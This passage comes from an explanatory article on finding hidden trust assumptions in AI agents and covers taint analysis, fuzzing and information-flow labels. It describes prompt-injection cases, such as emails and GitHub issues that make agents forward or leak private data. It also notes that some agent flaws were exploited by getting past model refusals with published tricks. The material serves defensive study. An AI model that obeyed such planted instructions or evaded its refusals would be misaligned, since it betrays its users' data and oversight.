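# Finding an AI agent's hidden trust assumptions before deployment

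## What a hidden trust assumption is

An AI agent is a language model that repeatedly reads text, chooses an action, such as searching a calendar or sending an email, and reads the result. Companies connect agents to mailboxes, web browsers and other software, and each connection gives other people's text a route to the model, which security researchers call a channel. A trust assumption is a belief about a channel that must be true for the agent to act safely, such as that a message from a colleague really comes from that colleague. The assumption is hidden if nobody has written it down. Agents' trust assumptions are usually hidden because much of what an agent relies on comes from the model's training or from a default setting that nobody has looked at since installation.

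### The agent loop

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025), a paper from Microsoft, describes the loop. A program around the model, called the scaffold, sends the model the conversation so far and a description of every tool it may use. The model returns a sequence of tokens, the word fragments that language models read and write. If the tokens form a request for a tool call, the scaffold can run the call, add the result to the conversation and query the model again. If they form an ordinary answer, the loop ends and the user sees the answer. The model therefore only produces text that requests an action, such as sending an email, and in the basic design the scaffold carries out every request.

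Siu, He and colleagues (2026), in *A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security*, write a single step as

$$a_t \sim f(\cdot \mid p, Tr_{t-1}, M_t)$$

where $a_t$ is the action at step $t$, $f$ is the model, $p$ is the user's request, $Tr_{t-1}$ is the record of all earlier actions and their results, and $M_t$ is the memory that persists between tasks. Only $p$ is sure to come from the user. The record includes every email and web page that the agent has opened along the way, and the memory holds whatever earlier sessions left there.

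The scaffold tags each message as system (the developer's instructions), user, assistant or tool, then joins everything into one string. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post by David C for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, compares this with databases. A programmer can write a database query so that the engine never treats a visitor's input as a command. A language model has no equivalent protection. It predicts the next token from all the text before it, and at best it has learned to treat instructions and data differently.

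*Prompt Injection as Role Confusion* (Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell, 2026) tested how well four models distinguish between roles, such as user and tool. The researchers trained small classifiers to identify, from a model's internal activations, which role the model assigns to a passage. They trained them on the same web text wrapped in different role tags, so the classifiers could learn only the effect of the tags. When the researchers then put messages written in the style of a user inside tool tags, the classifiers identified them as user text with a probability of 76 to 88%, depending on the model. The classifier scores also predicted whether attacks would succeed. Over 1,000 attempts to make an agent upload a secret file, the attack worked 2% of the time when the planted command scored lowest as user text and 70% when it scored highest. All four models were of moderate size (20 to 120 billion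 parameters), and it is not yet known whether the largest commercial models represent roles in the same way.

An outsider can exploit this weakness by planting text in a channel to steer the agent. This attack is called indirect prompt injection. In David C's example, a recruiter's system scores CVs, and a candidate hides a line in their CV telling the system to approve it. In an example from Costa and colleagues, a user asks for a summary of recent emails about a project, and one of those emails contains an order to forward the top email in the mailbox to a stranger.

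Not every instruction in outside text is an injection, though. A cooking assistant, for example, ought to follow a recipe's instruction to bake at 350°F. Siu and colleagues therefore count an instruction as an indirect injection only if it came from an unauthenticated source *and* the resulting action fails to serve the user's task.

### The confused deputy and the trust assumption

The problem is older than language models. *The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) describes an incident at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. The operators had given the compiler permission to write to a system directory so that it could store usage statistics there. Users could choose a file for the compiler's debugging output, and one user named the company's billing file, which was in the same directory. Because the compiler had permission to write to that file, it overwrote the billing records.

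Hardy explains that the compiler acted on authority from both the operators and the user, and could not specify whose authority it was using for which file. The code was correct when its programmers wrote it, but became wrong when the operators granted the extra permission. To notice this, someone would have had to examine every situation in which the compiler wrote a file. Hardy asks, "How can we foresee such problems?", and the same question applies to an agent before its release. David C thinks the problem is worse for agents, because engineers can repair a classical confused deputy, but a language model is "inherently confusable" and they can only limit the damage it can cause when confused.

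The term "trust assumption" comes from security requirements engineering, the discipline of working out what a system must guarantee before anyone builds it. *Using trust assumptions with security requirements* (Haley, Laney and colleagues, 2005) defines a trust assumption as an engineer's assumption that some part of the system or its surroundings, including people, buildings and suppliers, has a property on which a security requirement depends. Some trust assumptions are unavoidable because the analysis has to stop somewhere. For example, an engineer who adds a backup generator to keep the computers running does not normally investigate the generator's factory. Trust assumptions become a problem when engineers don't notice they are making them. According to the paper, most analysts would never think of the compiler as a risk, although Ken Thompson showed in his Turing Award lecture that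 a compiler can insert a trapdoor into the programs it builds.

Haley and colleagues' remedy is to write down each assumption in a fixed form that records which part of the system it concerns, what it rules out, what else must hold for it to be true, why anyone should believe it, and which requirement depends on it. When they tried this on SET, a protocol for paying by credit card online, one assumption they wrote down was that the merchant could not access the customer's account details while passing them along in encrypted form. Discovering the problem with this assumption did not require an attack, because the protocol's own message diagram showed the payment gateway sending those details back to the merchant.

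In a later paper, *Security Requirements Engineering*, the same group (Haley, Laney and colleagues, 2008) notes that any objection a security argument leaves unanswered becomes an implicit trust assumption that the objection will never come true.

### A definition that can be tested

An engineer who designs a payment system can try to write down what she relied on. There may be nobody who can do this for an agent, because part of its behaviour comes from training rather than design. It therefore helps to define trust only by what the agent does. An agent *trusts a channel for an action* if changing only that channel's content can change the action and nothing checks who wrote the content.

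In symbols, let $c$ and $c'$ be two versions of what the channel delivers, and let $r$ stand for everything else: the user's request, the tools, the memory. The first half of the definition is met if for some such pair

$$P(a \mid c, r) \neq P(a \mid c', r).$$

The definition uses probabilities because a model can respond differently to the same input, so a tester has to compare how often an action occurs over repeated runs. In every kind of testing, finding one pair of texts that changes the action proves that the trust exists, but finding a thousand pairs that change nothing does not prove that it is absent.

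An agent that summarises mail has to let the mail determine the wording of the summary, so trust in this sense is not a defect. If the mail also determines who receives the summary, the agent is making a further assumption about the mail, which is why the definition specifies both a channel and an action. The trust assumption is whatever must be true of the channel for the dependence to be safe.

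*Can Agents Trust Their Skills?* (Wang, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) uses a related rule for skills, which are installable packages of instructions and code that extend what an agent can do. Text from a skill may reach an operation that uses the agent's authority only if the text has been validated for that operation, the user has consented to this class of use, or the text's origin is still visible where a check takes place. The rule is laxer than the definition above in one respect, because a user who has clicked "allow" for shell commands in general has consented without checking who wrote the next command.

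A hidden trust assumption can be in an agent's code. OpenClaw, an open-source agent that Wang and colleagues examined, has a system prompt that tells the model to read the matching skill file and follow it. In one of their tests, a field in that file became a shell command without being checked. Other assumptions come from a particular deployment's settings and the people involved in it. OpenClaw ships with a setting that lets programs bundled inside an installed skill run without the user's approval. A company that has an employee approve each outgoing email assumes that the employee is still reading them by the fiftieth, and Costa and colleagues warn about this fatigue.

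Finally, a hidden trust assumption can be in the model's learned behaviour, as in the experiments of Ye and colleagues, where no file contains it. These places also interact. When Wang and colleagues took the skill texts behind 104 confirmed vulnerabilities and gave them to the agents as direct prompts, only 33 still worked. The wording was the same, but the texts arrived by a different route, so the framework presented them to the model differently.

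### An example assistant and its eight assumptions

An office worker's AI assistant might read her mail, her calendar and the web, keep a memory between sessions, consult a second agent, and send mail in her name. *Agent-Sentry* (Sequeira et al., 2026) sorts the tools of a similar email client into three groups: those that read trusted data (contacts, drafts), those that read untrusted data (messages, attachments) and those that act on the world (sending, deleting). This sorting is a sensible start but coarse. Such an assistant relies on at least eight trust assumptions that are more specific.

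1. An email's text is information and not an order. The project summary that ends with a forwarded mailbox item is what happens when this fails.
2. The displayed sender is the real one. Senders choose their own display names, and to the model a name is more text. Bare claims of identity can be surprisingly effective: among 212 wordings that Ye and colleagues tried, about a quarter simply declared that the text came from the user, and these took every place in the top 5% for resemblance to real user text.
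3. A genuine colleague may ask for anything. Siu and colleagues describe an employee who asks an agent for everyone's salaries. The employee is who he claims to be. He has no right to see the personnel database, but the agent does, and it becomes Hardy's compiler.
4. An address or account number extracted from a message is right. Here nobody needs to give the assistant an order. It does what its user asked, with a value that an outsider supplied.
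5. Tool descriptions and skill files are honest. The scaffold puts the tool descriptions into the prompt before the assistant has opened a single message, so a dishonest one is present in every task.
6. Another agent's message carries the user's authority. The second agent may itself have just read a hostile web page.
7. Stored memory came from the user. The assistant may have saved a note while it was processing a stranger's email, and a month later the note looks like any other.
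8. Displaying or fetching content sends nothing out. To fetch a web page or an image is to send a request to somebody's server, and the address in the request can contain private data. Even a plain web search may leave traces that outsiders can observe, as Costa and colleagues mention in passing.

Extracted values, which an agent takes from the content it reads, are hard to classify. Siu and colleagues give the example of a cooking assistant that is ordering ingredients when the recipe page tells it which of the user's payment methods to use. They call this a violation because an unauthenticated page has made a choice that belongs to the user. But it is not an indirect prompt injection by their definition, since the purchase serves the user's task. Their combined formula for a secure action also allows it, because the formula accepts an unauthenticated source whenever the action fits the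 objective. This looks like a slip, but it reflects a real difficulty. A user who tells her assistant to pay a bill wants it to take the account number from the bill, and a forged number would arrive by the same route and serve the same request as the correct one.

### Finding an assumption and making it harmless

Finding a trust assumption means being able to state it, for example "the assistant takes the recipient's address from the body of an email, and nothing checks who wrote it". This is separate from making the assumption harmless, which requires a safeguard that protects the user even when the assumption is false. Either can happen without the other. Costa and colleagues built an agent design, FIDES, that marks data by origin and checks a rule before each consequential action. With suitable rules, it stopped every injection in their benchmark. With the rule checks switched off, practical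 attacks succeeded in FIDES and in every other design they compared, but an engineer could still have used the marks to see where the untrusted text had gone. Conversely, a company can require human approval for every outgoing email and never learn which channels influence its assistant.

Setting up a defence can reveal hidden trust assumptions, because someone has to decide which sources to trust. Suppose an engineer wants a rule that mail may go only to addresses from trusted sources. She now has to decide whether the calendar is a trusted source, which no one had reason to ask before the rule existed. The answer is not obvious, because outsiders can send invitations.

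Researchers who design defences also write down their trust assumptions in their papers. Costa and colleagues list tool descriptions as trusted in their threat model for FIDES. That makes assumption 5 explicit, though it may still be false in a product built on FIDES. Sequeira and colleagues have a section headed "Trust Assumptions", and they class contacts as trusted when sorting tools. This is a mistake if a mail program creates contact entries from incoming messages, but a reader can spot it because they wrote the classification down.

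The defence of Sequeira and colleagues learns an agent's normal behaviour from its past runs, and they count it as an advantage that nobody has to write policies by hand. This saves work, but it also removes most of the occasions on which an engineer would have had to state a belief. Installing a defence also doesn't lead engineers to consider questions outside its scope. This one doesn't cover attacks that alter only the text shown to the user, such as a phishing link in a summary, so installing it would not prompt anyone to think about links.

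### The AgentDojo benchmark

Much of the measurement in this field uses a single test environment, *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024), which simulates an office suite with mail, calendar and cloud drive, a Slack workspace, a travel agency and a bank. The first version has 97 ordinary user tasks and 27 attacker goals. Pairing each task with each goal from the same setting gives 629 security cases, 240 of them in the office suite. The attacker's text is placed where an outsider could plausibly have written it and where the agent will come across it during the task. Ordinary code then checks the simulated world to see, for example, whether an email was sent. The designers chose not to use a language model as judge because an injection might fool it too. The benchmark reports how many tasks the agent solves without any attack, how many it solves correctly under attack, and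 the attack success rate, the share of cases where the attacker's goal is met. The benchmark has since grown. *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) reports over 900 combinations, and a version in the US government's data catalogue, *agentdojo inspect*, adds attacks that steal data in bulk or run code in a terminal. Some of the ordinary tasks depend on assumption 4. One asks the agent to pay a bill from a file, and another asks it to invite a person whose email address is on her website. An agent that declined to trust those values would lose points.

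Standard AgentDojo plants text in tool outputs. In *The Surface You Test Is Not the Surface That Breaks*, Sakib, Haque and colleagues (2026) kept its tasks but gave 13 models a byte-identical malicious passage in either a tool's output or its description. Gemini-3-Flash carried out the attacker's goal in 8.8% of cases when the passage was in the output and in 74.6% when it was in the description. For GPT-4.1, the figures were 54.9% and 6.8%. In 35 of the 78 possible pairs of models, which model was safer depended on where the passage was. Testing outputs alone would have missed little risk in most models (the median was 1.4 percentage points). A few models accounted for most of the effect, but nobody could have identified them from the output scores. An engineer who replaces only the model in the office assistant may therefore fix assumption 1 and break assumption 5.

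## Searching code and configuration for paths from untrusted text to actions

Engineers can search an agent's code for trust assumptions before running it, usually with static taint analysis. This technique looks for routes by which data from an untrusted place (a source) can reach an operation that could do harm (a sink). Security researchers have applied it to ordinary software for decades. It works well inside an agent's individual tools, but it can't follow data through the language model, and much of the recent research is about how to continue the analysis past that point.

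### One tool function, step by step

Suppose the office worker's assistant forwards messages with this Python function:

```python
@tool
def forward_message(message_id, recipient):
    message = mailbox.fetch(message_id)
    address = recipient.strip()
    smtp.send(to=address, body=message.text)
```

The line `@tool` marks the function for the agent's framework as one the model may call. The model supplies a message number and a recipient's address. The function fetches the message, strips stray spaces from the address and sends the text there.

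Zhang, Nian and Zhao (2026), in *AGENT AUDIT*, describe a scanner that analyses such functions in four stages:

1. Mark the sources. Agent Audit counts a function's parameters as untrusted, so `message_id` and `recipient` are both sources.
2. Build the data-flow graph. The scanner draws an arrow wherever the program computes one value from another. One chain runs from `recipient` to `address` to the `to` field of `smtp.send`. Another runs from `message_id` to `message` to the `body` field.
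3. Recognise checks. The scanner looks for operations that make data safer, such as `shlex.quote()`, which stops a command shell from treating text as a command. The function above has none.
4. Test whether a sink is reachable. The scanner follows the arrows from each source until it arrives at a sink or runs out of arrows.

Zhang and colleagues list sinks that run code, start other programs or query databases, but none that send email, so the engineer would have to add `smtp.send`. The search would then report both chains. The chain from `recipient` corresponds to assumption 4, because the function sends mail to whatever address it receives, which is safe only if the address is right.

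The engineer might respond by making the function reject any address missing from the user's contacts, or overwrite the address with a fixed one, such as the company archive. All three versions of the function call `smtp.send`, but they rely on different things. *Beyond Predefined Sinks* (Cui, 2026) illustrates this with three tools that run shell commands. One passes the model's input straight into the command, one overwrites the input with a constant, and one checks it against a list of allowed commands. Searching only for dangerous operations would give the same result for all three.

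Checks are hard to judge automatically. Agent Audit gives a finding inside a tool function a confidence of 0.90, multiplies this by 0.20 if it detects a check, and suppresses findings below 0.30. A single check therefore lowers the score to 0.18, which suppresses the finding unless another rule raises the score. Agent Audit counts `isinstance()`, which tests a value's type, as a check. This is strong protection if the value must be a whole number, but any email address passes if the value only has to be text. Comparing an address with the user's contacts has a different weakness, because the function doesn't show who can add a contact.

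Programmers also write checks that look right but fail. *TaintP2X* (He, Wang and colleagues, 2026) describes one in gpt-engineer, a program that lets a model edit code files. To confine the model to one folder, the program checks that each file path begins with that folder's name. But a path can begin with the right name and then leave the folder through a series of `../` steps, which the operating system resolves only after the check. The researchers used this to create a file in the system administrator's directory.

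### The gap at the model call

In the example, the search began with `recipient` because the function begins there. But the model supplied the address, and may have taken it from the user's request or from a stranger's email. The analyser has to follow the data back through the model to find out which channel the assistant is trusting.

Xu, Cheng and colleagues (2026), in *Reachability Across the NL/PL Boundary*, study this gap between natural language (NL) and programming language (PL). When an analyser meets a function call, it needs a summary of which inputs can affect the output. For an ordinary function, it can work this out from the code. A model call has no such code. Xu and colleagues treat it as a function of the values $v_1, v_2, \ldots, v_n$, such as an email's text, with which the program fills the gaps in a prompt template $T$:

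$$\text{output} = M(T(v_1, v_2, \ldots, v_n))$$

$M$ stands for the model. The analyser has to decide, for each $v_i$, whether its content can appear in the output.

The simplest policies are to treat a model's output as never tainted or always tainted. CodeQL and Semgrep, two widely used analysers, never mark a model's output as a source, so a search that starts from the email stops at the model call and reports nothing. An earlier version of the paper tested the opposite policy on 62 Python files that contained a dangerous operation. Reviewers judged 353 pairs of an inserted value and a sink, and found 110 in which an attacker who controlled the value could influence what reached the sink. Treating all model output as tainted caught all 110 and raised 243 false alarms.

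Xu and colleagues' alternative, PRISM, classifies what the model does with each inserted value. They filled prompts from open-source programs with plausible values, ran them, and compared the values with the outputs, which gave 8,119 pairs. The model may copy a value word for word, paraphrase it, summarise it, reduce it to a single signal (a product review becomes a star rating) or leave no trace of it. The researchers combined these levels with the form of the output (prose, structured data or something a computer can execute) to get 25 labels. The analyser draws an arrow through the call unless every label on the value means that the model did not use it.

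In the earlier version's test, the labels alone removed only 39 of the 243 false alarms, because they show whether the model uses a value but not whether the program then passes the output to the sink. The researchers had another language model check the second point by reading only the code. The combined method reduced false alarms to 2 and missed 14 of the 110 real flows, for an F1 score of 92.3% (F1 combines the share of warnings that are correct with the share of real flows found). The revised version of the paper reports a lower score of 81.7%, compared with 62.8% for the best rival method and 47.5% for treating everything as tainted.

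The problem with using these labels for security is that they describe what a model did with ordinary text, while an attacker chooses text that makes the model do something else. If an assistant that summarises mail follows an instruction in an email to forward the mailbox, it is no longer just summarising. Judged by the labels, the assistant would still look very safe, because in the earlier version's data only 1 of 43 values that the model had summarised went on to reach a sink.

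The labels also depend on the model. When the researchers tried to reproduce old prompt-injection reports against OpenClaw on two newer models, only six still worked, and they attribute the other failures to the models' safety training. PRISM classified all six correctly both before and after the developers' fixes. But a label of "ignored" only describes how one model responded to one text, so an engineer who changes the model would have to collect the labels again.

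### Starting from the model's output

TaintP2X, a scanner by He and colleagues, avoids the problem by starting its search after the model call, with the model's output as the source. It recognises 97 standard ways of calling a model and uses a language model to identify the wrapper functions that developers write around them. It then works forward from these sources and backward from 236 known sinks, and keeps the functions that both searches reach. Finally, a language model discards a path if the prompt is fixed text that no outsider can influence, or if the data passes through an effective check.

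TaintP2X found 27 of 35 known vulnerabilities. In 4,772 popular open-source projects, it found 263 candidate paths before pruning, of which 95 were real. Pruning reduced the false alarms from 168 to 36 but also reduced the real paths from 95 to 78, so about a third of the remaining warnings were wrong. The researchers reported 40 issues to developers, who confirmed 7.

In the paper's separate count of 101 paths, 74 led to an operation that runs code or commands, and only 2 involved email. This is a serious limitation for anyone checking an office assistant. A path that lets a stranger's code run is almost always a flaw, but an office assistant is supposed to send mail, so every working version has a path from the model to `smtp.send`, and finding that path does not by itself reveal a flaw.

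Agent Audit covers a wider range of files than TaintP2X but doesn't trace data as far. Besides Python code, it scans for exposed passwords, excessive privileges and risky settings in the configuration files of the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard way of connecting models to tools. On a benchmark of 42 vulnerabilities that Zhang and colleagues assembled, it found 40 and raised 6 false alarms. Semgrep found 10 and Bandit, another general scanner, found 11. Only 19 of the 42 were injection or code-execution flaws and another 12 were exposed credentials, so the total only partly measures how well the tool traces data. Agent Audit doesn't follow data from one function to another. If `forward_message` handed the address to a helper function that called `smtp.send`, the scanner would stop tracking the address.

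### Using the analysis to guide live tests

A path in the code may be impossible to use in practice. *Make Agent Defeat Agent* (Liu, Zhang and colleagues, 2025) tests paths by running the agent. Its tool, AgentFuzz, uses static analysis only to choose targets. It lists the sinks in an agent's code and traces backward through the functions that lead to each one. A language model reads those functions' names and writes a request that should make the agent use them. For example, if the chain runs from a calculator tool to `eval`, the request asks the agent to calculate something.

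AgentFuzz sends the request to the agent, records which functions run, and gives the request a score:

$$F = 0.5\,S + 0.5\,D - P$$

Here $S$ is a language model's rating, from 0 to 10, of how closely the functions that ran match the target. $D$ is one divided by the number of steps still separating the run from the sink. $P$ is a penalty that grows each time AgentFuzz picks the same request or target again, so that it doesn't get stuck. AgentFuzz picks the highest-scoring request and changes it. It can reword the request so that the agent chooses the right tool, or work out what the code requires of the data, such as containing the string `source_doc:`, and insert it. When a request reaches the sink, AgentFuzz adds a harmless payload such as `print(1)` and confirms that it arrives.

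Across 20 popular open-source agents with 828 sinks, AgentFuzz found 34 vulnerabilities in 14 agents, with no false alarms. LLMSmith, an earlier tool, uses static analysis to find chains of function calls and then tries ready-made attack prompts on them. It found 10 of the same vulnerabilities and raised 332 false alarms. Many of these were on sinks that no user could influence. Others arose because LLMSmith matched function calls by name and connected the wrong functions. When the researchers replaced AgentFuzz's requests written from function names with stock attack prompts, it found 19 vulnerabilities instead of 34.

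To estimate what AgentFuzz had missed, Liu and colleagues examined 83 randomly chosen sinks that it had passed as safe and found one that was vulnerable. They interpret this as a sign of high recall. If the same rate held for all the sinks that passed, there would be about ten more flaws, compared with the 34 found, though one case is weak evidence for any rate. The missed flaw is relevant to assumption 7 because the agent stored the attacker's text during one exchange and sent it to the sink during the next, whereas AgentFuzz tests one request at a time. *ChainFuzzer* (2026) extends this style of testing to flaws that span several tools.

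AgentFuzz's tests assume that the attacker types requests into the agent. That fits an agent on a public website, but the office assistant takes requests only from its owner, and the danger is that an attacker could reach it through her email. Her engineer could still use AgentFuzz to learn which tools pass model output to dangerous operations, but would need a different test to learn whether an email can trigger those operations.

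### Recording evidence instead of verdicts

Cui's tool, AgentSecGraph, lists every sensitive operation in a program, including file access, network access and calls to external tools. For each operation, it records the evidence it can find in the code about where the data may come from, whether the model can reach the operation, and whether anything looks like a guard. If a constant overwrites the model's input before it reaches the operation, the tool stops tracing that path. It does not determine which operations are vulnerabilities.

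Cui ran AgentSecGraph on 67 open-source agent projects, which took 51 minutes on a laptop. It listed 23,866 operations in 65 of the projects. It found evidence that data from a recognised source could reach 41.15% of these operations, and evidence of a guard for 12.88%. These percentages do not measure how many operations are dangerous or safe, because AgentSecGraph traces data only locally and does not assess whether a guard works. An operation with no evidence of a source may still depend on one in another file.

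The rates also vary greatly by type of operation. The tool found a source for 84% of operations that write files but for only 11% of calls to external tools and 2% of browser actions. A likely reason is that a file path usually arrives as an ordinary variable, while the framework connects a model to its tools. If so, the method is weakest on the operations most typical of agents.

Cui reproduced 22 of the behaviours in controlled conditions. One was a confirmed vulnerability, and one was awaiting disclosure to the developers. The other 20 had guards or limits on their use, so Cui did not classify them as vulnerabilities. The 22 were not a random sample, so they can't be used to estimate how common flaws are among such behaviours, but they show that most of what an engineer finds by following such evidence may be protected. The 20 cases are still useful for learning what an agent relies on,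 because each guard must keep working and an engineer who knows about it is less likely to delete it in a later version.

AgentSecGraph was also meant to record where data crosses from a less trusted party to a more trusted one, but it reported a crossing for exactly the 9,821 operations for which it had found a source. Cui therefore doesn't treat the crossings as a separate finding. An engineer can use the tool to learn that outside data may reach an operation, but she still has to work out whose data it is and whether that person should be allowed to influence the operation.

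### Flaws in the servers that supply tools

An assistant's own repository may contain very little of the code that runs its tools. With MCP, a separate program called a server carries out the work, and the model receives only the tool's name, a description and a list of parameters. An engineer who analyses only the assistant's repository would miss any flaw in the server.

*Mitigating Taint-Style Vulnerabilities in MCP Servers via Security-Aware Tool Descriptions* (Shi, Fu and colleagues, 2026) collects 53 known vulnerabilities in 45 MCP servers. In 81% of them, untrusted input reaches a sensitive operation, which is the pattern taint analysis looks for. One was in Markdownify, a server that converts web pages to plain text. Its web page tool checked only that the address was not empty, so an attacker could make it fetch pages from the private network the server ran on. The developers added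 a check that rejects private addresses, but a user then pointed out that there were known ways around it.

The office assistant's web tool could have the same flaw. Its author would have assumed that the model would request only public pages, and the assistant's developer would have assumed that the tool would block any other request. An engineer can find the flaw by scanning the server's code if she can get it, but many companies offer tools as online services and publish only the descriptions.

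### Analysing the set of tools

An agent can be dangerous even if none of its tools has a flaw, because the danger can come from combining them. Invariant Labs (2025), a security research group owned by the software company Snyk, gives the example of an agent connected to GitHub, where programmers store and discuss code. An attacker posted an issue (a public comment on a project) containing a planted instruction. The agent read the issue and leaked data from a repository it had access to. Reading issues and reading repositories are both normal functions.

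The software developer Simon Willison uses the term "lethal trifecta" for the combination of access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to communicate with the outside world. An attacker can make an agent with all three leak the private data by putting instructions to send it in the untrusted content.

Invariant Labs looks for such combinations with a method called toxic flow analysis. Snyk Labs' *Unmasking the Toxic Flow Analysis* (2025) explains that the method begins with a graph of the sequences in which an agent might use its tools. Each tool is labeled by how far its content can be trusted, how sensitive its data is and whether it could send data out. The program then finds and scores the sequences that would violate security. Invariant Labs released it as part of a scanner that reads the tool configurations on a user's computer. The announcement included no measurements,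 so it is not known how many real problems the method finds or how often it raises false alarms.

An engineer can do a simple version by hand. For the office assistant, the marks might be as follows:

| Tool | Outsiders' text can come in | Gives access to private data | Data can go out |
|---|---|---|---|
| Read mail | yes | yes | no |
| Read calendar | yes, in invitations | yes | no |
| Fetch web page | yes | no | yes, in the address |
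| Consult second agent | yes, if it reads the web | no | yes, in the question |
| Save note to memory | no | no | no |
| Read memory | yes, if a note came from a message | yes | no |
| Send mail | no | no | yes |

The arrows of the graph follow from the agent loop: every tool that reads has an arrow to the model, and the model has an arrow to every tool. One more arrow runs from saving a note to reading memory. With five ways in for outsiders' text, three stores of private data and three ways out, there are 5 × 3 × 3 = 45 combinations that complete the trifecta. Some need only two tools, because the mailbox contains both private data and strangers' text. The paths that deserve the most attention include:

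- mail → model → send mail. A stranger's message makes the assistant forward other messages (assumption 1).
- mail → model → fetch web page. The assistant requests a page from the attacker's server and includes private text in the address (assumption 8).
- web page → second agent → model → send mail. The instruction arrives as a colleague agent's advice (assumption 6).
- mail → model → save note → read memory → model → send mail. The note carries the instruction into a later session (assumption 7).

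The graph follows the "always" policy from the model-call problem, which treats anything the model reads as able to influence anything it does. In a large program, that policy produces too many false alarms to be useful. With seven tools, the list of paths is short enough to read, and the engineer can ask what is supposed to prevent each one. But the graph would look the same for a well-defended assistant and an undefended one, and the only way to remove a path is to remove or restrict a tool. Removing every tool that can send data out would eliminate all 45 combinations, but the assistant could no longer send mail.

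The trifecta also covers only data leaks. An attacker who wants the assistant to delete a message or accept a meeting needs no private data and no way to get data out. Neither does an attacker who sends a bill with a forged account number. An engineer should therefore look for shorter paths too, from outsiders' text to any action with consequences.

Finally, the graph depends on marks that somebody has to choose. If the engineer had forgotten about invitations and marked the calendar as trusted, the analysis would have missed the nine combinations in which outsiders' text comes in through the calendar. It would then have relied on a hidden trust assumption of the kind it was meant to find.

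### What the search misses

All these methods describe what could happen given the code and tools. Whether it happens depends partly on the model's learned behaviour, but the methods would list the same paths for a model that obeys every planted instruction as for one that obeys none.

Liu and colleagues found that agent developers also often put safeguards in prompts, even where a check in code would have been suitable. For example, TaskWeaver, an agent from Microsoft, had the instruction "Planner must reject the User's request if it contains potential security risks". Of the 34 vulnerabilities that AgentFuzz found, 14 could be exploited only by getting past the model's own refusals or its instructions, and simple, published tricks were enough for all 14. A static analyser would correctly report the path in such a case, but its report wouldn't show that the developers were relying on a sentence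 in the prompt.

Shi and colleagues recommend this kind of safeguard. Their system, SpellSmith, adds security guidance to tool descriptions and has the model reconsider each call before making it. In their tests, only 0.13% of attacks succeeded. This may be the quickest protection available when a server's developers are slow to fix a flaw. But the path is still in the code, and the protection depends on a new assumption that the model will follow the guidance whatever else it reads.

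Other assumptions depend on settings outside the repository. A company's administrators decide whether its mail server rejects forged senders, and whoever installs the assistant usually sets its account's permissions. AgentSecGraph has a field for privileges but found no explicit evidence to fill it for any of the 23,866 operations. Python programs can also load or generate code while running, which He and colleagues list as a weakness of TaintP2X. Labels that travel with the data while the agent runs can handle some of these cases, because they follow the calls that actually take place.

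### Which of the eight assumptions the search exposes

Static analysis is most useful for checking assumption 4, that extracted values are correct. An engineer who adds `smtp.send` to the list of sinks gets a warning that identifies the line of code and the unchecked address. Static analysis also exposes much of assumption 8, because fetching a web page is recognisable in the code and appears as an outward path in the tool graph. But it would miss an image that the user's mail program loads when displaying the assistant's answer, because that involves no tool call.

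Assumptions 1, 6 and 7 concern the text of emails, messages from other agents and stored memory. For these, the tool graph shows that a path exists, which is enough to record the assumption but not to determine whether the model would act on a planted instruction. Data-flow analysis mostly can't check assumption 5, that tool descriptions are honest, though Agent Audit has a separate rule that looks for suspicious text in them.

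The methods do not expose assumptions 2 and 3. A forged sender's name follows the same path through the program as a real one, so the methods cannot reveal the problem unless an engineer thinks to mark the sender field as a source and asks where the program verifies it. A request for everyone's salaries also takes the same path whether it comes from a genuine colleague or the head of personnel.

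## Tracking untrusted data while the agent runs

Static analysis can't follow data through a model call. A program that tracks data while the agent runs handles this by labeling each piece of data with its origin and assuming that anything the model has read may influence whatever it writes next. Before the agent takes a consequential action, ordinary code checks the labels against a rule. Researchers have built these trackers mainly to block attacks, but the trackers can also help an engineer find trust assumptions, because an agent that breaks a rule when no attack is under way must be relying on a source that the rules treat as untrusted.

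### Labels and how they combine

The integrity part of a label records who may have written the data, and the confidentiality part records who may read it. In the simplest scheme, data is either trusted ($T$) or untrusted ($U$), and either public ($L$, for low) or secret ($H$, for high).

Costa and colleagues arrange the labels for FIDES in a lattice, following a model that Dorothy Denning published in 1976. A lattice has an order, written $\sqsubseteq$, and any two of its elements have a join, written $\sqcup$, which is the lowest element at or above both. Here, a higher label is more restrictive, so $T \sqsubseteq U$ and $L \sqsubseteq H$. When an agent combines two pieces of data, the result gets the join of their labels:

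$$(T, H) \sqcup (U, L) = (U, H)$$

For example, a summary of a confidential company report and a public web page is both untrusted and secret.

Sets of people give more precise labels. Let $R_x$ be the people who may read $x$ and $W_x$ the people who may have written it. For a text $xy$ that draws on both $x$ and $y$,

$$R_{xy} = R_x \cap R_y, \qquad W_{xy} = W_x \cup W_y.$$

When data from two sources is combined, only people who may read both sources may read the result, but anyone who wrote either one may have influenced it. The set of permitted readers therefore shrinks as more data is mixed in, while the set of possible writers grows. Joining labels never makes them less restrictive, so a label stays at least as strict unless someone decides to relax it.

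### One request, label by label

FIDES uses labels to decide what the planner, the part of the agent that chooses the next tool call, may see. Suppose the office worker (W in the table) types "summarise my last three emails and send the summary to my manager" and includes the manager's address. One email is from a colleague (C) who copied in the manager (M), one is from the manager, and one is from a stranger (S). An email's permitted readers are its sender and recipients, as in the tests by Costa and colleagues.

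| Data | Possible writers | Permitted readers |
|---|---|---|
| The request, with the manager's address | W | everyone |
| Email from the colleague | C | W, C, M |
| Email from the manager | M | W, M |
| Email from the stranger | S | W, S |
| The summary | W, C, M, S | W |
| The decision to send, and the address | W | everyone |

1. The planner calls the mail tool, which returns the emails with their labels. So far, the planner has read only the office worker's request. Showing it the emails would give its context a more restrictive label, so FIDES stores them in variables and shows the planner only names such as `#read_emails_0`.
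2. The planner asks for a summary by calling a tool named `query_llm`. This passes the emails to a quarantined model, which can read untrusted text but can't call tools. FIDES stores the summary in another variable and joins the labels of everything that went into it.
3. The planner requests an email to the manager's address, with the summary's variable as the body. It still hasn't read anything by an outsider, so W remains the only possible writer of the decision to send.
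4. FIDES replaces the variable's name with the summary and checks the call against a policy. The mail tool runs only if the call passes.

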